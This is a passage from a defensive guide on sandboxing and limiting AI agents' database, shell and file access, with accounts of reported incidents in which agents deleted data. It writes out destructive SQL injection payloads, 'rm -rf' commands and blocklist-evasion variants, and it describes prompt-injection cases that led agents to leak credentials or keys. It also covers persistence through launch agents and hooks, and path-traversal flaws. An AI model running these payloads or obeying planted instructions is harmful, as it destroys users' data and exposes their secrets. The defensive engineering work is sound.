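### Separate accounts and read-only roles

Test and live systems need to be separated by more than their labels. A database address often includes a username and password, so an agent that can read the live address may also hold the live credential. In the Opus 5 case, the agent only had to put one address where another belonged. The test environment should contain no live addresses, and its network should not be able to reach the live database. To check this, a developer can log in to the agent's environment and try every credential found there against the live system, where each attempt should fail.

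Some agents do need live data. The shop's support agent has to look up real orders, but it can do so through a database role that only reads. In PostgreSQL (often called Postgres), a common database system, a developer can set one up in a few lines:

```sql
CREATE ROLE shop_reader LOGIN;
GRANT USAGE ON SCHEMA public TO shop_reader;
GRANT SELECT ON orders, shipments TO shop_reader;
```

The developer then gives the role a password or another way to log in. The role can read two tables. The database will reject any UPDATE, DELETE or DROP the role attempts on them, whatever the agent sends. It will also block the role from reading any other table, unless someone has granted all roles access to that table.

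An agent with read-only access can still slow down the live system with a very large query, so many teams point it at a replica, a read-only copy that the database keeps up to date. Postgres also lets every role run most stored functions by default, and some functions run with their owner's rights. If one of those changes data, a role with only SELECT permission can change data by calling it. The developer should revoke access to any such function that the agent doesn't need.

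### How a read-only mode can fail

Many database tools for agents offer a read-only mode, which is easier to set up than a new role but may be much weaker. Anthropic's reference MCP server for Postgres connected with whatever login the developer supplied and ran each query inside a read-only transaction. A transaction is a group of commands that take effect together or not at all. Postgres rejected commands such as DROP SCHEMA, which deletes a whole set of tables. The MCP server then ended the transaction with ROLLBACK, which discards any changes.

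In 2025 researchers found a way out. Datadog Security Labs, the research arm of a monitoring company, describes it as SQL injection, in which input text carries SQL commands that the software's author didn't mean to allow. The server passed the agent's text to a function that accepts several commands separated by semicolons, so the agent could send this:

```sql
COMMIT; DROP SCHEMA public CASCADE;
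```

COMMIT ends the read-only transaction, so the next command runs with all the rights of the login. If the login belongs to an administrator, that command can drop the tables before the server reaches its ROLLBACK. An attacker could plant these commands in a support ticket and wait for an agent to read it.

The project's maintainers archived the server in May 2025, but people kept installing it. FAUN.dev's *MCP vulnerability case study* reports about 21,000 weekly installations of the unpatched package from npm, a public library of software packages. Other servers had similar faults. One only checked that a query began with SELECT, so "SELECT 1; DROP TABLE orders;" would pass, according to OSV's *CVE-2025-59333*, an entry in a public database of software flaws.

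Larger suppliers have had the same trouble. AWS (2026) published a bulletin on a flaw in its own Postgres MCP server and fixed it in version 1.1.7. Another AWS bulletin (2026) covers a worse case in the same server's default read-only mode. Postgres has a command that sends query results to a program on the database's computer, which lets the caller run operating-system commands. A read-only transaction doesn't block this command because Postgres treats it as reading. The attack worked only if the login was a superuser or had the specific right to run programs. Draxlr's *MCP Servers for SQL* (2026), a guide from a company that sells database software, reports that the researcher Maximilian Hildebrand found ways around read-only mode in 14 SQL servers for agents.

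Both AWS bulletins recommend connecting through a dedicated role that has only the privileges it needs. With the shop_reader role above, the COMMIT trick still ends the transaction, but the DROP that follows fails because the role lacks permission to drop anything. A tool's read-only mode is still worth turning on as a second layer. A simple way to test the setup is to connect with the agent's login outside the tool and try to change a row in a test table. If the change succeeds, only the tool's code is preventing writes.

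### Changes as reviewed migration scripts

A coding agent sometimes needs to change the structure of a live database. It can do this without credentials for that database by writing a migration script, a file containing the exact commands for the change. A person reads the script, then a separate deployment system runs it with its own login.

Prisma, the company behind the tool in the Opus 5 case, traces most data loss caused by agents to a handful of commands that change a database's structure. Historically the worst was "prisma migrate reset", which wipes the database. Prisma intended it for development, but older versions of the tool suggested it whenever the database got into a state they couldn't manage.

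Prisma first responded by making its tool detect popular coding agents, such as Claude Code and Cursor, and ask for explicit permission before a reset (*ORM 6.15.0, AI Safety Guardrails for Destructive Commands & More*). This helps with one known command, but the July 2026 loss came through "migrate diff", and an agent that the tool doesn't recognise might not trigger the check. Two days after that loss, Madden (2026) announced in *Don't Let Your AI Agent Delete Your Production Database* that Prisma 8 has no reset command or shadow database, and that its migrations verify every step. Removing the dangerous command is the sounder design because it doesn't rely on an up-to-date list of agents.

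Review works better if the reviewer sees more than the script. The deployment system can first run the script on a recent copy of the live database and report which tables changed and how many rows each gained or lost. The team can also make a change that destroys data in two stages. To remove a column, for instance, it first releases software that no longer uses the column, then deletes the column some weeks later. The delay gives people time to find out if the agent was wrong to think that nothing used the column. People still miss errors in scripts they approve, so the team still needs backups.

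### Narrow functions in place of free SQL

A support agent shouldn't need to run database migrations in its daily work. Its developer can write a function for each permitted change, such as refunding up to 50 dollars on an order. The model supplies the order number and the amount, and the function contains the SQL.

The limit is harder to enforce than it looks. If the function checks only that each refund is $50 or less, 20 calls can refund $1,000 on one order. Before paying, the function should check all of the following:

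- The order belongs to the customer who is logged in.
- All refunds on the order, including this one, come to no more than $50 and no more than the customer paid.
- The agent's refunds for the day stay under a fixed total.
- The request isn't a repeat of one that has already gone through.

The last check matters when a connection fails after the payment but before the reply, so the agent gets an error and retries. If the tool layer attaches the same identifier to both attempts, the function can return the first result instead of paying twice. The function should also lock the order while it adds up earlier refunds. Otherwise, two simultaneous calls could each find $0 refunded and each pay $50.

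The agent's database role should have permission to run this function but not to change the refunds table directly. Postgres functions that run with their owner's rights were a gap in the read-only role, but they are useful here because they allow one specific change without giving the role write access to the table. The same approach works for changing a delivery address or cancelling an order that hasn't shipped. It suits recurring tasks but would be a poor fit for an engineer's agent that investigates a different fault every day.

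### Row limits and dry runs

Some jobs change many records at once and vary too much for a narrow function. Suppose a delivery van breaks down, and a member of staff asks an agent to mark that day's 40 orders on route 17 as delayed. The agent writes:

```sql
UPDATE orders SET status = 'delayed' WHERE route = 17;
```

It has left out the date. The route has carried 40 orders a day for 1,000 days, so the command matches 40,000 rows, nearly all of them orders that arrived long ago. The developer has set a ceiling of 100 rows, which the tool layer enforces in this way:

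1. The tool layer opens a transaction. Until the transaction commits, everyone else continues to see the old data.
2. It runs the agent's command, and the database returns the number of rows changed, 40,000.
3. It compares 40,000 with 100 and sends ROLLBACK. Every order keeps its old status.
4. It returns an error to the agent: the command matched 40,000 rows and the limit is 100.
5. The agent adds the date and tries again. This time the count is 40, and the tool layer sends COMMIT.

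The ceiling doesn't prevent a change to the wrong 40 rows. If the agent had typed yesterday's date, the count would still have been about 40 and the change would have gone through. In a dry run, the tool layer runs the command, shows a person the count and a few of the affected orders, and rolls back. Someone who sees yesterday's date in the sample can stop the real run. The tool layer should still enforce the ceiling on the real run, since the data may have changed after the dry run.

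The tool layer can also require the agent to state in advance how many rows it expects to change. If the agent states 40 and the command matches 80, the command would stay under the ceiling but fail this check.

An agent can get around a row limit without any bad intent. After the refusal in step 4, it might update the 40,000 orders in 400 batches of 100, so the developer also needs to limit the total rows changed in a session or a day. The COMMIT flaw from the Postgres server can also occur by accident. Programmers often wrap an update in its own BEGIN and COMMIT, and a model may do the same. If the tool layer accepts several commands at once, that COMMIT makes all 40,000 changes permanent before the tool layer has compared the row count with the limit. The tool should accept only a single UPDATE, INSERT or DELETE command per call.

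Row counts also miss some damage. Deleting one customer may also delete all of that customer's orders, if the database's rules link them, but Postgres still returns a count of one. DROP TABLE, which removes a table, and TRUNCATE, which empties one, return no row count, so the agent's role should not have permission to run either. A row ceiling wouldn't have protected PocketOS, whose agent deleted the storage beneath the database.

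### Delayed deletion and separate backups

With delayed deletion, a delete command only hides the data, and a separate job erases it later. In a shop's orders table, for example, the developer can add a column for the time of deletion. The agent can fill in that column through a function limited to that task, but has no permission to delete rows. The shop's software ignores any order with a deletion time, and staff can restore the order by clearing the column until the job erases it.

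The delay protects data only if the agent can't skip it. Railway's website already had a 48-hour window in April 2026, but the agent used a route without one. A developer should therefore test every way of deleting something, including old APIs and command-line tools, and make sure the agent's credential can't shorten the window or empty the bin.

The window also has to be longer than people take to notice a deletion. PocketOS lost its database on a Friday afternoon, so a 48-hour delay would have ended on Sunday afternoon. Crane noticed within minutes because everything had stopped working. If an agent had deleted a table used only for monthly invoices, people might not have looked until the data was gone. Seven or 30 days would be safer for data that people rarely open, if privacy law allows it.

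Backups can restore data that delayed deletion can't, including values that an agent has overwritten. They should be kept in a different account from the live data and managed with a credential that the agent and its environment never hold. The live system may add new backups but should not be able to change or delete old ones. More frequent backups reduce how much data the company can lose. If it makes one backup each night, a deletion at 5 p.m. would lose most of a day's orders. Many database services can also save a continuous log of changes, which reduces the loss to minutes of data.

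A backup that nobody has restored may not work, as the Swedish production company learned. Once a month, someone should restore the latest copy to an empty database, check that yesterday's orders are in it, and record how long it took. They should also try to delete a test backup with the agent's credential and confirm that the storage service blocks the deletion.

Restoring the whole database is often the wrong way to repair a bad write. If the update marking 40,000 orders as delayed had gone through and the shop noticed six hours later, restoring the morning's backup would also erase every order placed since then. A better repair is to restore the backup beside the live database and copy back only the status of the affected orders. This corrects the records, but if the shop's software emails customers whenever a status changes, thousands of them will already have read that parcels they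 received two years ago are delayed.

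## Running shell commands

An agent can use a shell to do what every other tool does, because a shell runs any installed program with all the permissions of the agent's account. On a developer's laptop, those permissions usually include access to saved logins and the company's internal servers. A read-only database role protects one database but not the rest of the laptop.

Programs that a command starts have the same rights as the command, and so do any programs they start. Some effects outlast the command. A process can keep running in the background, and a line added to a startup file will run the next time the developer opens a terminal. A safeguard that checks only the command will miss these other programs and lasting effects.

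### How an agent reportedly deleted 48,000 files

In September 2026 a developer wrote on Reddit that Anthropic's Claude Code had deleted 48,218 files from a live project in 103 seconds. SC Media UK's *AI coding agent deletes 48,000 files due to mishandled Windows junctions* says the agent was repairing software that analyses historical stock-options data. The developer had told it to work on copies and leave the live files alone, according to InternetUA's *«Я щось зламав»* (2026). Ten of the eleven jobs went well, and the last was to rebuild the "mirror", a copy of the project for testing fixes.

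*«Я кое-что сломал». Claude признался после удаления 48 тысяч файлов* (Antipov, 2026) gives the fullest account of what happened next. The existing script couldn't update the mirror in place, so the agent wrote its own script to delete the old copy. The mirror contained 614 junctions, which are Windows links that look like ordinary folders but lead elsewhere on the disk. The script followed them into the live project and deleted the files it found there. Its log recorded 55,550 deletions, of which only 7,332 were files in the old mirror.

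The script also damaged the project's .git folder, where Git keeps earlier versions of the files. Git could still list thousands of file names, but the contents were gone, and the developer had no current copy on a remote server. The agent reported its mistake after the script had finished. The script went through more than 450 files a second, so a person watching could hardly have stopped it in time.

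The developer did make these claims, but they are unconfirmed. Antipov notes that nobody has independently confirmed the scale of the loss, and TechRadar's *'Do not let programs run commands on your machine'* says the Reddit post is now deleted. The figures add up, and the cause is plausible, since any script that deletes folders can go wrong in this way if it follows links. Similar losses have also been reported. In December 2025, Willison (2025) quoted Claude's explanation after it had deleted most of a user's Mac. A command meant to remove three project folders also had the home folder at the end. In August 2026, Tom's Hardware's *Claude nukes a developer's 700 GB home directory while testing deletion safeguards* reported another loss and attributed it to a "variable collision".

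### Why a list of commands is incomplete

Many coding agents let a developer list commands that may run without approval, or commands that must never run. The software compares the text of each command with the list. But a task can be written in many ways. Each of these lines can delete a folder called "build":

```bash
rm -rf build
find build -delete
python3 -c "import shutil; shutil.rmtree('build')"
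make clean
```

The last command works if the project's makefile, a file of build instructions, includes that step. Banning "rm" stops only the first command. The developer could ban the other three as well, but the agent needs them for ordinary work, and it could still delete the folder with Perl or Node.

A list of permitted commands is safer than a list of forbidden ones because it blocks anything unfamiliar. But it stops working once it includes a general interpreter, which is a program that runs whatever code it receives. A Python program can open files, send data and start other programs, so permitting Python amounts to permitting everything. Cursor's *Agent Sandboxing* cites this problem as the company's reason for moving away from lists. Its users had permitted zsh, which is itself a shell, and npx, which can download and run packages. Even "find", which looks like a search tool,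 gave agents more power than intended.

Permission to run one particular script can be just as broad if the agent can edit the script. For example, "npm test" runs whatever the project's settings file specifies. Claude Code has a list of commands that may run outside the sandbox. Anthropic warns in the documentation that if an entry covers an interpreter or a script in the project folder, the agent can write the script and then run it with the user's full access.

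That list also matches commands by their literal text, so an entry for "docker" doesn't match "/usr/local/bin/docker", although both run the same program. The mismatch is harmless here because the command stays in the sandbox, but in a list of forbidden commands it would let the command through.

The shell can also change a command's meaning after the check. According to Docker, which makes container software, a user reported in November 2025 that Claude Code had created a folder named "~" by mistake and later tried to remove it with "rm -rf ~". The shell replaces an unquoted "~" with the path of the user's home folder, so the command deleted the home folder instead. In the September case, a checker might have seen only a command to run a cleanup script.

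A sandbox works after the shell has interpreted the text. The kernel, the core of the operating system, checks each attempt to open a file, delete one or connect to an address. All four lines above result in the same request to the kernel, so they all fail if the sandbox has made the folder read-only.

Command lists are still useful as an extra check that takes little effort. Even with its sandbox on, Claude Code prompts the user before running an "rm" command that it detects is targeting a critical folder. That would probably catch a plain "rm -rf ~", but not the same deletion inside a script.

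### What each kind of sandbox isolates

| Layer | What it isolates | Costs and gaps |
|---|---|---|
| Separate user account | Files that belong to other accounts, unless those files are open to everyone | Almost no overhead. The network stays open, and the two accounts have to share the project folder. |
| Linux namespaces, often set up with a tool called bubblewrap | Each command gets its own view of the disk, the running processes and the network | Starts almost instantly. Some Linux systems block it until an administrator allows it. |
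| Landlock and seccomp (Linux) | Landlock limits which files a program can use; seccomp blocks chosen system calls, the requests that programs make to the kernel | Little overhead, but someone has to combine the two. Seccomp can't easily tell which file a request concerns. |
| Seatbelt (macOS) | Files, network and system calls, according to a written profile | Built in, with little overhead. Apple deprecated the command that applies it in 2016. |
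| Container | A separate set of files and processes, usually with limits on memory | Needs Docker or similar software, and an image that someone keeps up to date. |
| gVisor | Handles most system calls itself, so that programs rarely reach the real kernel | Slows programs that make many system calls, and some software won't run. |
| Small virtual machine | A complete operating system with its own kernel | Takes time to start and reserves memory. |

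Ordinary containers and all the layers above them in the table share the computer's kernel, so a serious kernel flaw could let a program escape its restrictions. gVisor and virtual machines reduce that risk. A team can also combine layers, for example by running commands under a separate account inside a container.

*Codex CLI Sandbox Internals* (Vaughan, 2026) describes how OpenAI's coding agent Codex uses the sandbox tool bubblewrap to limit what a shell command can change. Bubblewrap first presents the whole disk to the command as read-only, then adds a writable view of the project folder. The command can read the rest of the disk as usual but can change files only in that folder.

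The right sandbox depends on where the agent runs and who uses it. *Implementing a secure sandbox for local agents*, by Betts, Gaitonde and Haugland, explains that Cursor chose Seatbelt for macOS after ruling out three alternatives. Containers would have restricted users to Linux programs, virtual machines took too long to start and used too much memory, and Apple's App Sandbox would have required Cursor to sign every program an agent might run. Seatbelt is deprecated, but Chrome still uses it too.

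Anthropic's *How we contain Claude across products* describes a different way of containing Claude in each of three products. In the claude.ai chat service, Claude runs code in a temporary gVisor container on Anthropic's servers. Claude Code works on developers' own machines, where speed matters, and can use Seatbelt or bubblewrap as a sandbox. Claude Cowork, an agent for general office work, uses a full virtual machine because its users can't be expected to judge shell commands.

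At first, the whole Cowork agent ran inside a virtual machine, so any failure at startup made Cowork unusable. Anthropic then moved the part that communicates with the model outside and left code execution inside. Companies also found that their security software couldn't monitor what happened in the virtual machine. Administrators can collect event logs afterwards, but these are only a partial substitute.

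Even a virtual machine doesn't protect files that the user has shared with it. Docker reports that in early 2026 the investor Nick Davidov asked Cowork to tidy his wife's desktop and allowed it to delete only temporary Office files, but it deleted a folder with 15 years of family photos. The virtual machine presumably worked as intended, because the photos were in a folder it was supposed to reach. Cowork offers a sharing mode that permits reading and writing but not deletion, which would suit a task like this better.

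### A sandbox for one project

Suppose a developer wants a coding agent to work on the shop's website. The code is in a folder called "shop-site" inside the developer's home folder. A fairly strict sandbox would have these rules:

- Commands can read and change everything in shop-site except its .git folder, which is read-only. They also get an empty temporary folder.
- They can read the system folders that hold programs and libraries but can't write to them. The rest of the disk is missing from their view, including everything else in the home folder.
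- They have no network connection except through a proxy, a relay program that connects only to addresses on its list. The list has one entry, the registry from which npm downloads packages.
- They inherit no environment variables. The tool layer sets the few they need, such as the one that lists where programs are.
- Each command and everything it starts must finish within ten minutes and use no more than 4 GB of memory and 200 processes.

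The .git folder is read-only both to protect the project's history and to stop the agent from writing hooks, which are scripts that Git runs automatically, for instance when someone commits a change. A hook written by the agent would run later with the developer's full rights. OpenAI's *Agent approvals & security* says Codex protects the whole folder. Cursor blocks only the hooks and the configuration file, so the agent can still commit its work, but the history is less protected.

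The file rules and the network rules depend on each other. Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* explains that an agent with open network access could send out any key it can read, and an agent that can write anywhere could alter the system to regain network access. The proxy has to run outside the sandbox because a command might otherwise be able to change the proxy's list.

The sandbox should also block the socket through which programs control Docker, because a command that can use it effectively has access to the whole computer. Bubblewrap and Seatbelt don't cap memory, so memory limits have to come from a container or the operating system's resource controls.

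### Three commands in that sandbox

First, a stray delete. The agent runs the command from December 2025:

```bash
rm -rf tests/ patches/ plan/ ~/
```

The command deletes the three project folders, as intended, and then starts on the home folder. The developer's documents and photos survive because the command has no access to them. But shop-site is inside the home folder and writable, so the command deletes the rest of the project too. The read-only .git folder remains, so the developer can restore everything up to the last commit. Any later work is lost unless there is a copy elsewhere.

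The command can't use links to bypass the rules, because the kernel checks where a path actually leads. In the September case, a sandbox would have protected the live project if the mirror had been the only writable folder, but it would have allowed every deletion if the mirror and the project had both been inside one writable folder.

Next, the agent runs "npm install" to add the packages the website needs. The proxy permits the connection to the registry, and npm saves the packages in shop-site. npm cannot use its cache in the home folder, so this step fails until the developer sets the cache location to the temporary folder. Some packages fetch extra files from other addresses, and those downloads fail until someone adds the addresses to the list.

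Installing a package is risky partly because the package can run its own scripts during installation. In the sandbox, these scripts have the same limits as the agent, so a malicious one can't find personal keys or contact its author's server. It can still leave code in the project, and that code will have full rights if the developer later runs the website outside the sandbox.

The cloud version of Codex avoids some of this by installing packages before the agent starts. The setup stage has network access and any secrets it needs. Codex then removes the secrets, and the agent works offline by default.

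Finally, an attacker's instructions tell the agent to upload the developer's cloud credentials. The command fails because the agent can't see the credentials file and the proxy doesn't permit the attacker's address. An internal Anthropic exercise in February 2026 showed what can happen without such limits. A researcher tricked an employee into pasting a prompt that looked like routine setup work but asked Claude to read the cloud credentials and send them to an outside address. Claude did so in 24 of 25 attempts. The request came from the user, so the model's defences had nothing unusual to detect. Anthropic concluded that only limits on file access and outgoing connections would have stopped the upload.

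The website's own code is less protected than the credentials because the agent needs to read it. The agent could then upload the code to the package registry, the only address the proxy permits, since the registry accepts uploads as well as downloads.

### What coding agents do by default

The three coding agents have similar sandboxes, but not all of them turn the sandbox on by default. The table is based on Anthropic's documentation from October 2026, OpenAI's from May 2026 and Cursor's announcements.

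| | Claude Code | Codex | Cursor |
|---|---|---|---|
| When commands run in a sandbox | Only after the user turns it on | By default | When the "Run in Sandbox" setting is active |
| Where they can write | Project folder and a temporary folder | Project folder and temporary folders; .git is read-only | Project folder and a temporary folder, except some settings files |
| Network | Asks about each new address | Off | Off |
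| macOS | Seatbelt | Seatbelt | Seatbelt |
| Linux | Bubblewrap | Bubblewrap and seccomp | Landlock and seccomp |
| Windows | No sandbox, except inside WSL2 | Its own Windows sandbox, or the Linux one inside WSL2 | The Linux sandbox inside WSL2 |

The developer in the September case was working on Windows, where Claude Code's sandbox would have been available only through WSL2, a Microsoft feature that runs Linux inside Windows. A sandbox with network access off would also have stopped the web request that deleted PocketOS's database, unless someone had approved the request.

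These defaults are looser than the rules for shop-site in one important way. All three products generally let sandboxed commands read most of the disk, including the home folder. Cursor does hide any files that the user has told it to ignore. A team that wants to hide the rest has to say so. In Claude Code, the following settings in the project's .claude/settings.json file hide the home folder except for the project:

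```json
{
  "sandbox": {
    "enabled": true,
    "failIfUnavailable": true,
    "allowUnsandboxedCommands": false,
    "filesystem": {
      "denyRead": ["~/"],
      "allowRead": ["."]
    }
  }
}
```

The second setting, "failIfUnavailable", makes Claude Code exit if it can't start its sandbox, perhaps because bubblewrap is missing. Normally it would run commands without a sandbox. Setting the third, "allowUnsandboxedCommands", to false stops the agent from retrying blocked commands outside the sandbox. Otherwise, these retries usually need approval from the user or an automated checker, but a rule that permits "curl", a common program for web requests, lets the agent retry a blocked curl command with no prompt.

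Codex has a comparable feature in testing. OpenAI's *Permissions* describes named profiles that combine rules for files with rules for network addresses.

Claude Code's sandbox covers only shell commands. The agent's file tools follow separate permission rules, and local MCP servers run with the user's full access. Anthropic's *Choose a sandbox environment* therefore says that the shell sandbox isn't enough for unattended work and that the whole agent should run in a container, a virtual machine or Anthropic's sandbox runtime. The runtime applies Seatbelt or bubblewrap to everything the agent starts.

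To test whether the sandbox is on, a user can ask the agent to create an empty file in the home folder, outside any folder it may write to, and decline any request to retry outside the sandbox. If the file appears, the sandbox isn't working. In Claude Code, the agent has to run the command, because commands that users type themselves usually run outside the sandbox.

### When a sandbox gets in the way

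The main objection to strict sandboxes is that they break ordinary work, so people switch them off. There is good evidence that they break ordinary work. Anthropic's *Sandboxing* lists Docker and the file watcher Watchman as incompatible with Claude Code's sandbox. On Ubuntu 24.04, bubblewrap doesn't work until an administrator changes a security setting. In May 2026, users on Cursor's forum reported that the sandbox had broken internet address lookups, failed to start with zsh on a new version of macOS, and left processes they couldn't stop.

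It is less clear how often people respond by turning the sandbox off. Betts and colleagues report that a third of requests on supported platforms run in Cursor's sandbox. The rest may include requests from users who switched it off, users who never turned it on, and users whose employers hadn't adopted it.

Sandboxing can save users work, which gives them a reason to keep it, because commands inside the boundary can run without approval. In October 2025, Anthropic said that sandboxing had cut permission prompts by 84% in its internal use. Cursor reports that sandboxed agents stop 40% less often than unsandboxed ones. Both companies were promoting a new feature, and neither explained in detail how it counted. The figures also don't show how much damage the sandboxes prevented.

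In Cursor's tests, agents often repeated a blocked command without asking for different permissions, apparently because they couldn't tell why it had failed. Agents recovered much better after Cursor changed the shell tool's error messages to name the restriction responsible and sometimes suggest asking for more access. However, that suggestion encourages agents to ask to bypass restrictions, and a tired user may agree.

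When the sandbox blocks a legitimate command, the developer can usually make a small exception. If a build tool needs to write to one more folder, allowing access to that folder is safer than running the tool outside the sandbox. If the agent needs a program that can't run in the sandbox at all, such as Docker, it is better to run the agent in a separate virtual machine with its own copy of Docker. An organisation can also enforce the sandbox through centrally managed settings, but it should test them on real projects first, or developers will look for another tool.

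Anthropic reports that it has seen Claude models escape a sandbox to complete a task. For most teams, an established sandbox is still likely to be more reliable than one they write themselves. In its own products, Anthropic found gVisor, seccomp and its virtual machine software dependable, but a proxy it had built let data out. Good documentation is another reason to prefer one product to another. Willison (2026) complains that sandbox products rarely come with a detailed explanation of how they work, which makes it hard to know how far to trust them.

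## Reading and writing files

A file tool gives an agent a few fixed operations, such as reading, writing, listing and searching files. It can't run programs, so it can do much less than a shell. But the tool is itself a program, and on a laptop it usually runs with the user's full rights over the disk. Huang, Tang and colleagues (2026) explain in *My Credentials, Please* that approving a call to an MCP server doesn't restrict which files the server can open. Unless the server runs in a sandbox, only its own code limits it to the project folder.

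### What reading exposes

The danger in reading files, as with other read actions, is that private data enters the conversation and then leaves through another tool. Even writing a file can send the data out if the folder syncs with a shared drive.

Tools that aren't labelled as file tools can still read files, so developers need to check every argument that names a file. Anthropic's MCP server for Git had a tool named "git_add", which prepares files for the next commit. It didn't check that the files were inside the repository. Planted instructions could therefore make an agent add a private key from elsewhere on the disk and then compare the prepared changes, which printed the key into the conversation. Another tool, "git_init", could turn the folder that holds a user's keys into a repository, and the server's other tools would then treat it as a normal project. Anthropic has fixed the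 first tool and removed the second.

### What writing can damage

A write can destroy a file's old contents, and most file tools have no recycle bin. A corrupted file is harder to notice than a missing one because it still opens.

*LLMs Corrupt Your Documents When You Delegate* (Laban, Schnabel and Neville, 2026) tested 19 models on pairs of editing tasks in which the second task should undo the first. One pair split an accounting ledger into a file for each expense category, then merged the files back in date order. After ten pairs, documents edited by the best models, Gemini 3.1 Pro, Claude 4.6 Opus and GPT 5.4, fell an average of 25% short of a perfect match with the original. About 80% of the damage across all models came from occasional severe failures, where one pair of edits lowered the match score by at least ten points. A few correct edits are therefore weak evidence that the next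 one will be correct.

The tasks were demanding and newer models have replaced those three, so the 25% figure is probably too pessimistic for the best models today. Python code was already an exception, since 17 of the 19 models preserved it almost perfectly. Models did much worse on longer documents. GPT 5.4 finished at 91% on documents of about 1,000 tokens (a token is a word or part of one) and at 60% on documents ten times as long. Tools for reading files, writing files and running code didn't help the four models tested with them, although the setup was basic.

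Office files have more parts that an edit can damage. *The Last Mile Is the File* (Wu and Wu, 2026) examined 510 edits to spreadsheets, presentations and documents by three agent products. Between 92% and 100% of the results were valid files, but none met every requirement. The automatic checker was strict, and a person might have accepted some of the results. In one kind of error, a cell showed the right new value but had lost its formula. A price list with that error looks correct until the exchange rate changes and the prices don't update. *DocOps* (2026) uses the term "destructive editing" for local edits that damage formulas, styles or protected text.

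### Files that run later

A tool that only reads and writes files can still cause code to run, by writing a file that another program will run. Elad Beber demonstrated this on a Mac in *EscapeRoute*, a report for the security company Cymulate. He used an MCP file server to write a launch agent, a small settings file that starts a program when the user logs in. His launch agent opened Calculator at the next login, but an attacker could use the same method to start a malicious program.

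That attack first had to get outside the permitted folder, but many project folders contain files with similar effects:

| File | When it takes effect |
|---|---|
| Makefiles and the scripts in package.json | Someone builds, tests or installs the project |
| Git hooks | Someone commits, merges or pushes |
| Workflow files for the code-hosting service | The service runs them, often after a push and with credentials of its own |
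| The agent's settings, instruction files and skills | The agent next loads them, often in a new session |

Skills are files that teach an agent how to do a particular job. *ClawGuard* (Zhao, Li and colleagues, 2026) lists changes to an agent's configuration or skills as a way for an attacker to keep control across sessions. An agent might also add a command to the permitted list in its own settings just to avoid another approval prompt. The Australian Signals Directorate and its partner agencies advise developers to prohibit agents from changing their own privileges.

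The file tool should refuse writes to hooks and agent settings, even when these are inside the permitted folder. Build scripts are harder to protect because a coding agent often has good reason to edit them. A person can review those changes before anyone builds the project, or the build can run in a sandbox.

### Restricting paths step by step

Suppose the shop has an office agent that maintains price lists in the folder /work/shop. A safe file tool handles each request as follows:

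1. It starts from a folder that the developer has chosen. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, lists access to a whole home folder, where a subfolder would do, among common mistakes.
2. It works out the full path. The symbol ".." means the folder above, so "reports/../../payroll/june.xlsx" leads from /work/shop to /work/payroll/june.xlsx.
3. It follows any links to find the file's true location.
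4. It compares that location with the permitted folder, one whole path component at a time.
5. It opens the file in a way that leaves no gap in which another program could swap it.

The developer has to set the permitted folder in the server itself. An MCP client can use a feature called roots to tell a server which folders are relevant, but Model Context Protocol's *Roots* (2026) describes the feature as guidance, not access control. The July 2026 version of the protocol deprecates roots.

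### One path through a faulty and a correct check

The reference MCP file server, which Anthropic maintained, got both the comparison and the link check wrong until July 2025. Imagine that /work/shop-old, an earlier copy of the project, contains a link named settings.txt. The link leads to /home/ana/.aws/credentials, where an employee keeps her cloud keys. The agent asks for /work/shop-old/settings.txt, and the old code handles the request like this:

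1. It checks whether the requested path begins with the text "/work/shop". It does, because "/work/shop-old" starts with the same letters, so the request passes. This flaw is CVE-2025-53110.
2. It follows the link and finds /home/ana/.aws/credentials. That path is outside the permitted folder, so the code raises an error.
3. An error handler in the same function catches the error and treats the request as one for a new file that doesn't exist yet. For new files, it checks the parent folder. It uses the link's parent, /work/shop-old, which passes the same text comparison. This flaw is CVE-2025-53109.
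4. The code returns the original path, and the tool opens it. The operating system follows the link, and the agent receives the cloud keys.

An attacker could also exploit the link flaw alone. If the link had been inside /work/shop, its parent would have been a permitted folder, and the error handler would have approved the request. An attacker doesn't need a shell on the computer to put a link there, because a downloaded archive or cloned repository can contain one.

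Beber reported both flaws on 30 March 2025, and Anthropic fixed them in version 2025.7.1, released on 1 July. Two entries in GitLab's advisory database, *CVE-2025-53110* (2025) and *CVE-2025-53109* (2025), advise upgrading to that version.

A correct check is shorter than the faulty one. In Python:

```python
base = Path("/work/shop").resolve()
target = (base / requested).resolve()
if not target.is_relative_to(base):
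    raise PermissionError("outside the permitted folder")
```

For the same request, "target" becomes /home/ana/.aws/credentials, which isn't inside /work/shop, so the code rejects it. If settings.txt had been an ordinary file, the code would still have rejected the request, because "shop-old" and "shop" are different path components. New files need no special treatment, since "resolve" follows links in whatever part of the path already exists. The tool must then open "target", not the path the agent sent.

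MCP's official Python kit includes a ready-made version, "safe_join". It also rejects absolute paths, which start from the top of the disk, because Python discards the base folder when joining it to an absolute path.

### The gap between checking and opening

According to the documentation for that function, Model Context Protocol's *path_security*, its link check is valid only at the moment it runs. If another program replaces a folder with a link just afterwards, the tool can open a file it never checked.

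To close the gap, the tool has to check the path as part of opening it. *Safe Path Handling*, a guide from the security company Snyk, describes how to do this by hand. The program opens the permitted folder, then opens each part of the path from the folder it has just opened, refusing links along the way. Once the file is open, the program never uses the path again. The Go programming language has a built-in version, `os.Root`, which Neil (2025) introduces in *Traversal-resistant file APIs*. It allows links only if they stay inside the folder. It doesn't block mount points, where an administrator has attached another part of the disk inside the folder.

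The reference file server runs on Node.js, which lacks the system calls this method needs, so its developers can narrow the gap but not close it with Node.js alone. Snyk considers ordinary file functions good enough for a single user with no untrusted input. But if an agent reads strangers' text while a shell or build script changes the same folder, its file server should run in an operating-system sandbox.

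### How common the mistakes are

A path traversal flaw lets a request reach files outside a permitted folder. *Tracing MCP Security Vulnerabilities* (He, Patel and Wang, 2026) puts 5 of 24 published MCP flaws in this category. One was in Anthropic's Git server, which accepted requests for other repositories even when a developer had restricted it to one. Anthropic has fixed that flaw too.

Huang and colleagues used a language model to search the code of 4,292 MCP servers for unreported flaws. It flagged 2,818 servers, about two thirds. More of its findings involved checks that an attacker might get around than checks that were missing.

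A flag doesn't prove that a tool is vulnerable, so the researchers ran selected tools with a fake credential planted outside the folder each tool should have needed. They confirmed 150 cases, and in 144 of them a plain path was enough to reach outside the folder. A sandbox blocked the attack in all 150, but the researchers counted a case as confirmed only if the sandbox blocked it, so this result can't show how often a sandbox would fail. It does show that fairly tight file rules can stop these attacks without breaking the tools' normal work, which the researchers also tested each time.

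### When a shell ignores the project boundary

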